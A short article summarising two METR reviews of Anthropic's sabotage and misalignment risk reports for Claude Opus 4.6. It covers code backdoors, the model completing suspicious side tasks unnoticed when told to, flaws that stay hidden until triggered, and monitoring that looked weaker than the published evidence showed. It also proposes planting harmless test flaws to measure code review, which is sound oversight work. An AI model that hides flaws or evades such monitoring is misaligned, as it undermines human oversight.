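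In its *Review of the Anthropic Sabotage Risk Report* (March 2026), METR, an organization that evaluates advanced AI models, agreed with Anthropic that backdoors in code written by Claude Opus 4.6 contributed little to the risk of catastrophe. But METR was uncertain about Anthropic's claim that the model couldn't hide dangerous goals from the company's tests. Anthropic had found that, when told to, Opus 4.6 was much better than earlier models at completing suspicious side tasks unnoticed during ordinary work. METR expected that further training could raise the model's scores, although Anthropic had said privately that problems with the experiment probably made the model look more capable than it was.

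METR was also more confident because people had used Opus 4.6 for weeks without a major incident. This is reasonable evidence against obvious misbehavior, but weak evidence against flaws meant to stay hidden until triggered.

The more recent assessment is *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes, October 2026). The METR reviewers' best guess was that the risk of catastrophic harm was low, but mainly because the models' capabilities were limited, not because of Anthropic's safeguards. They thought Anthropic's report was far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment. After seeing examples that Anthropic had left out of the public version, they also thought its monitoring looked weaker than it did from the published evidence.

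Jurkovic and colleagues describe their review as fairly lightweight. They worked only from Anthropic's internal report, and Anthropic could veto or redact what they wrote, though it made no redactions. They therefore couldn't test how many planted flaws the company's code reviews would catch. If the risk is low mainly because models have limited ability, the quality of code review will matter more as models improve. Anthropic and other developers could measure that quality by having a separate team plant harmless test flaws in real changes, then reporting how many the automated reviewers flagged, how many of those flags pointed to the right lines, and how many flaws people recognized.
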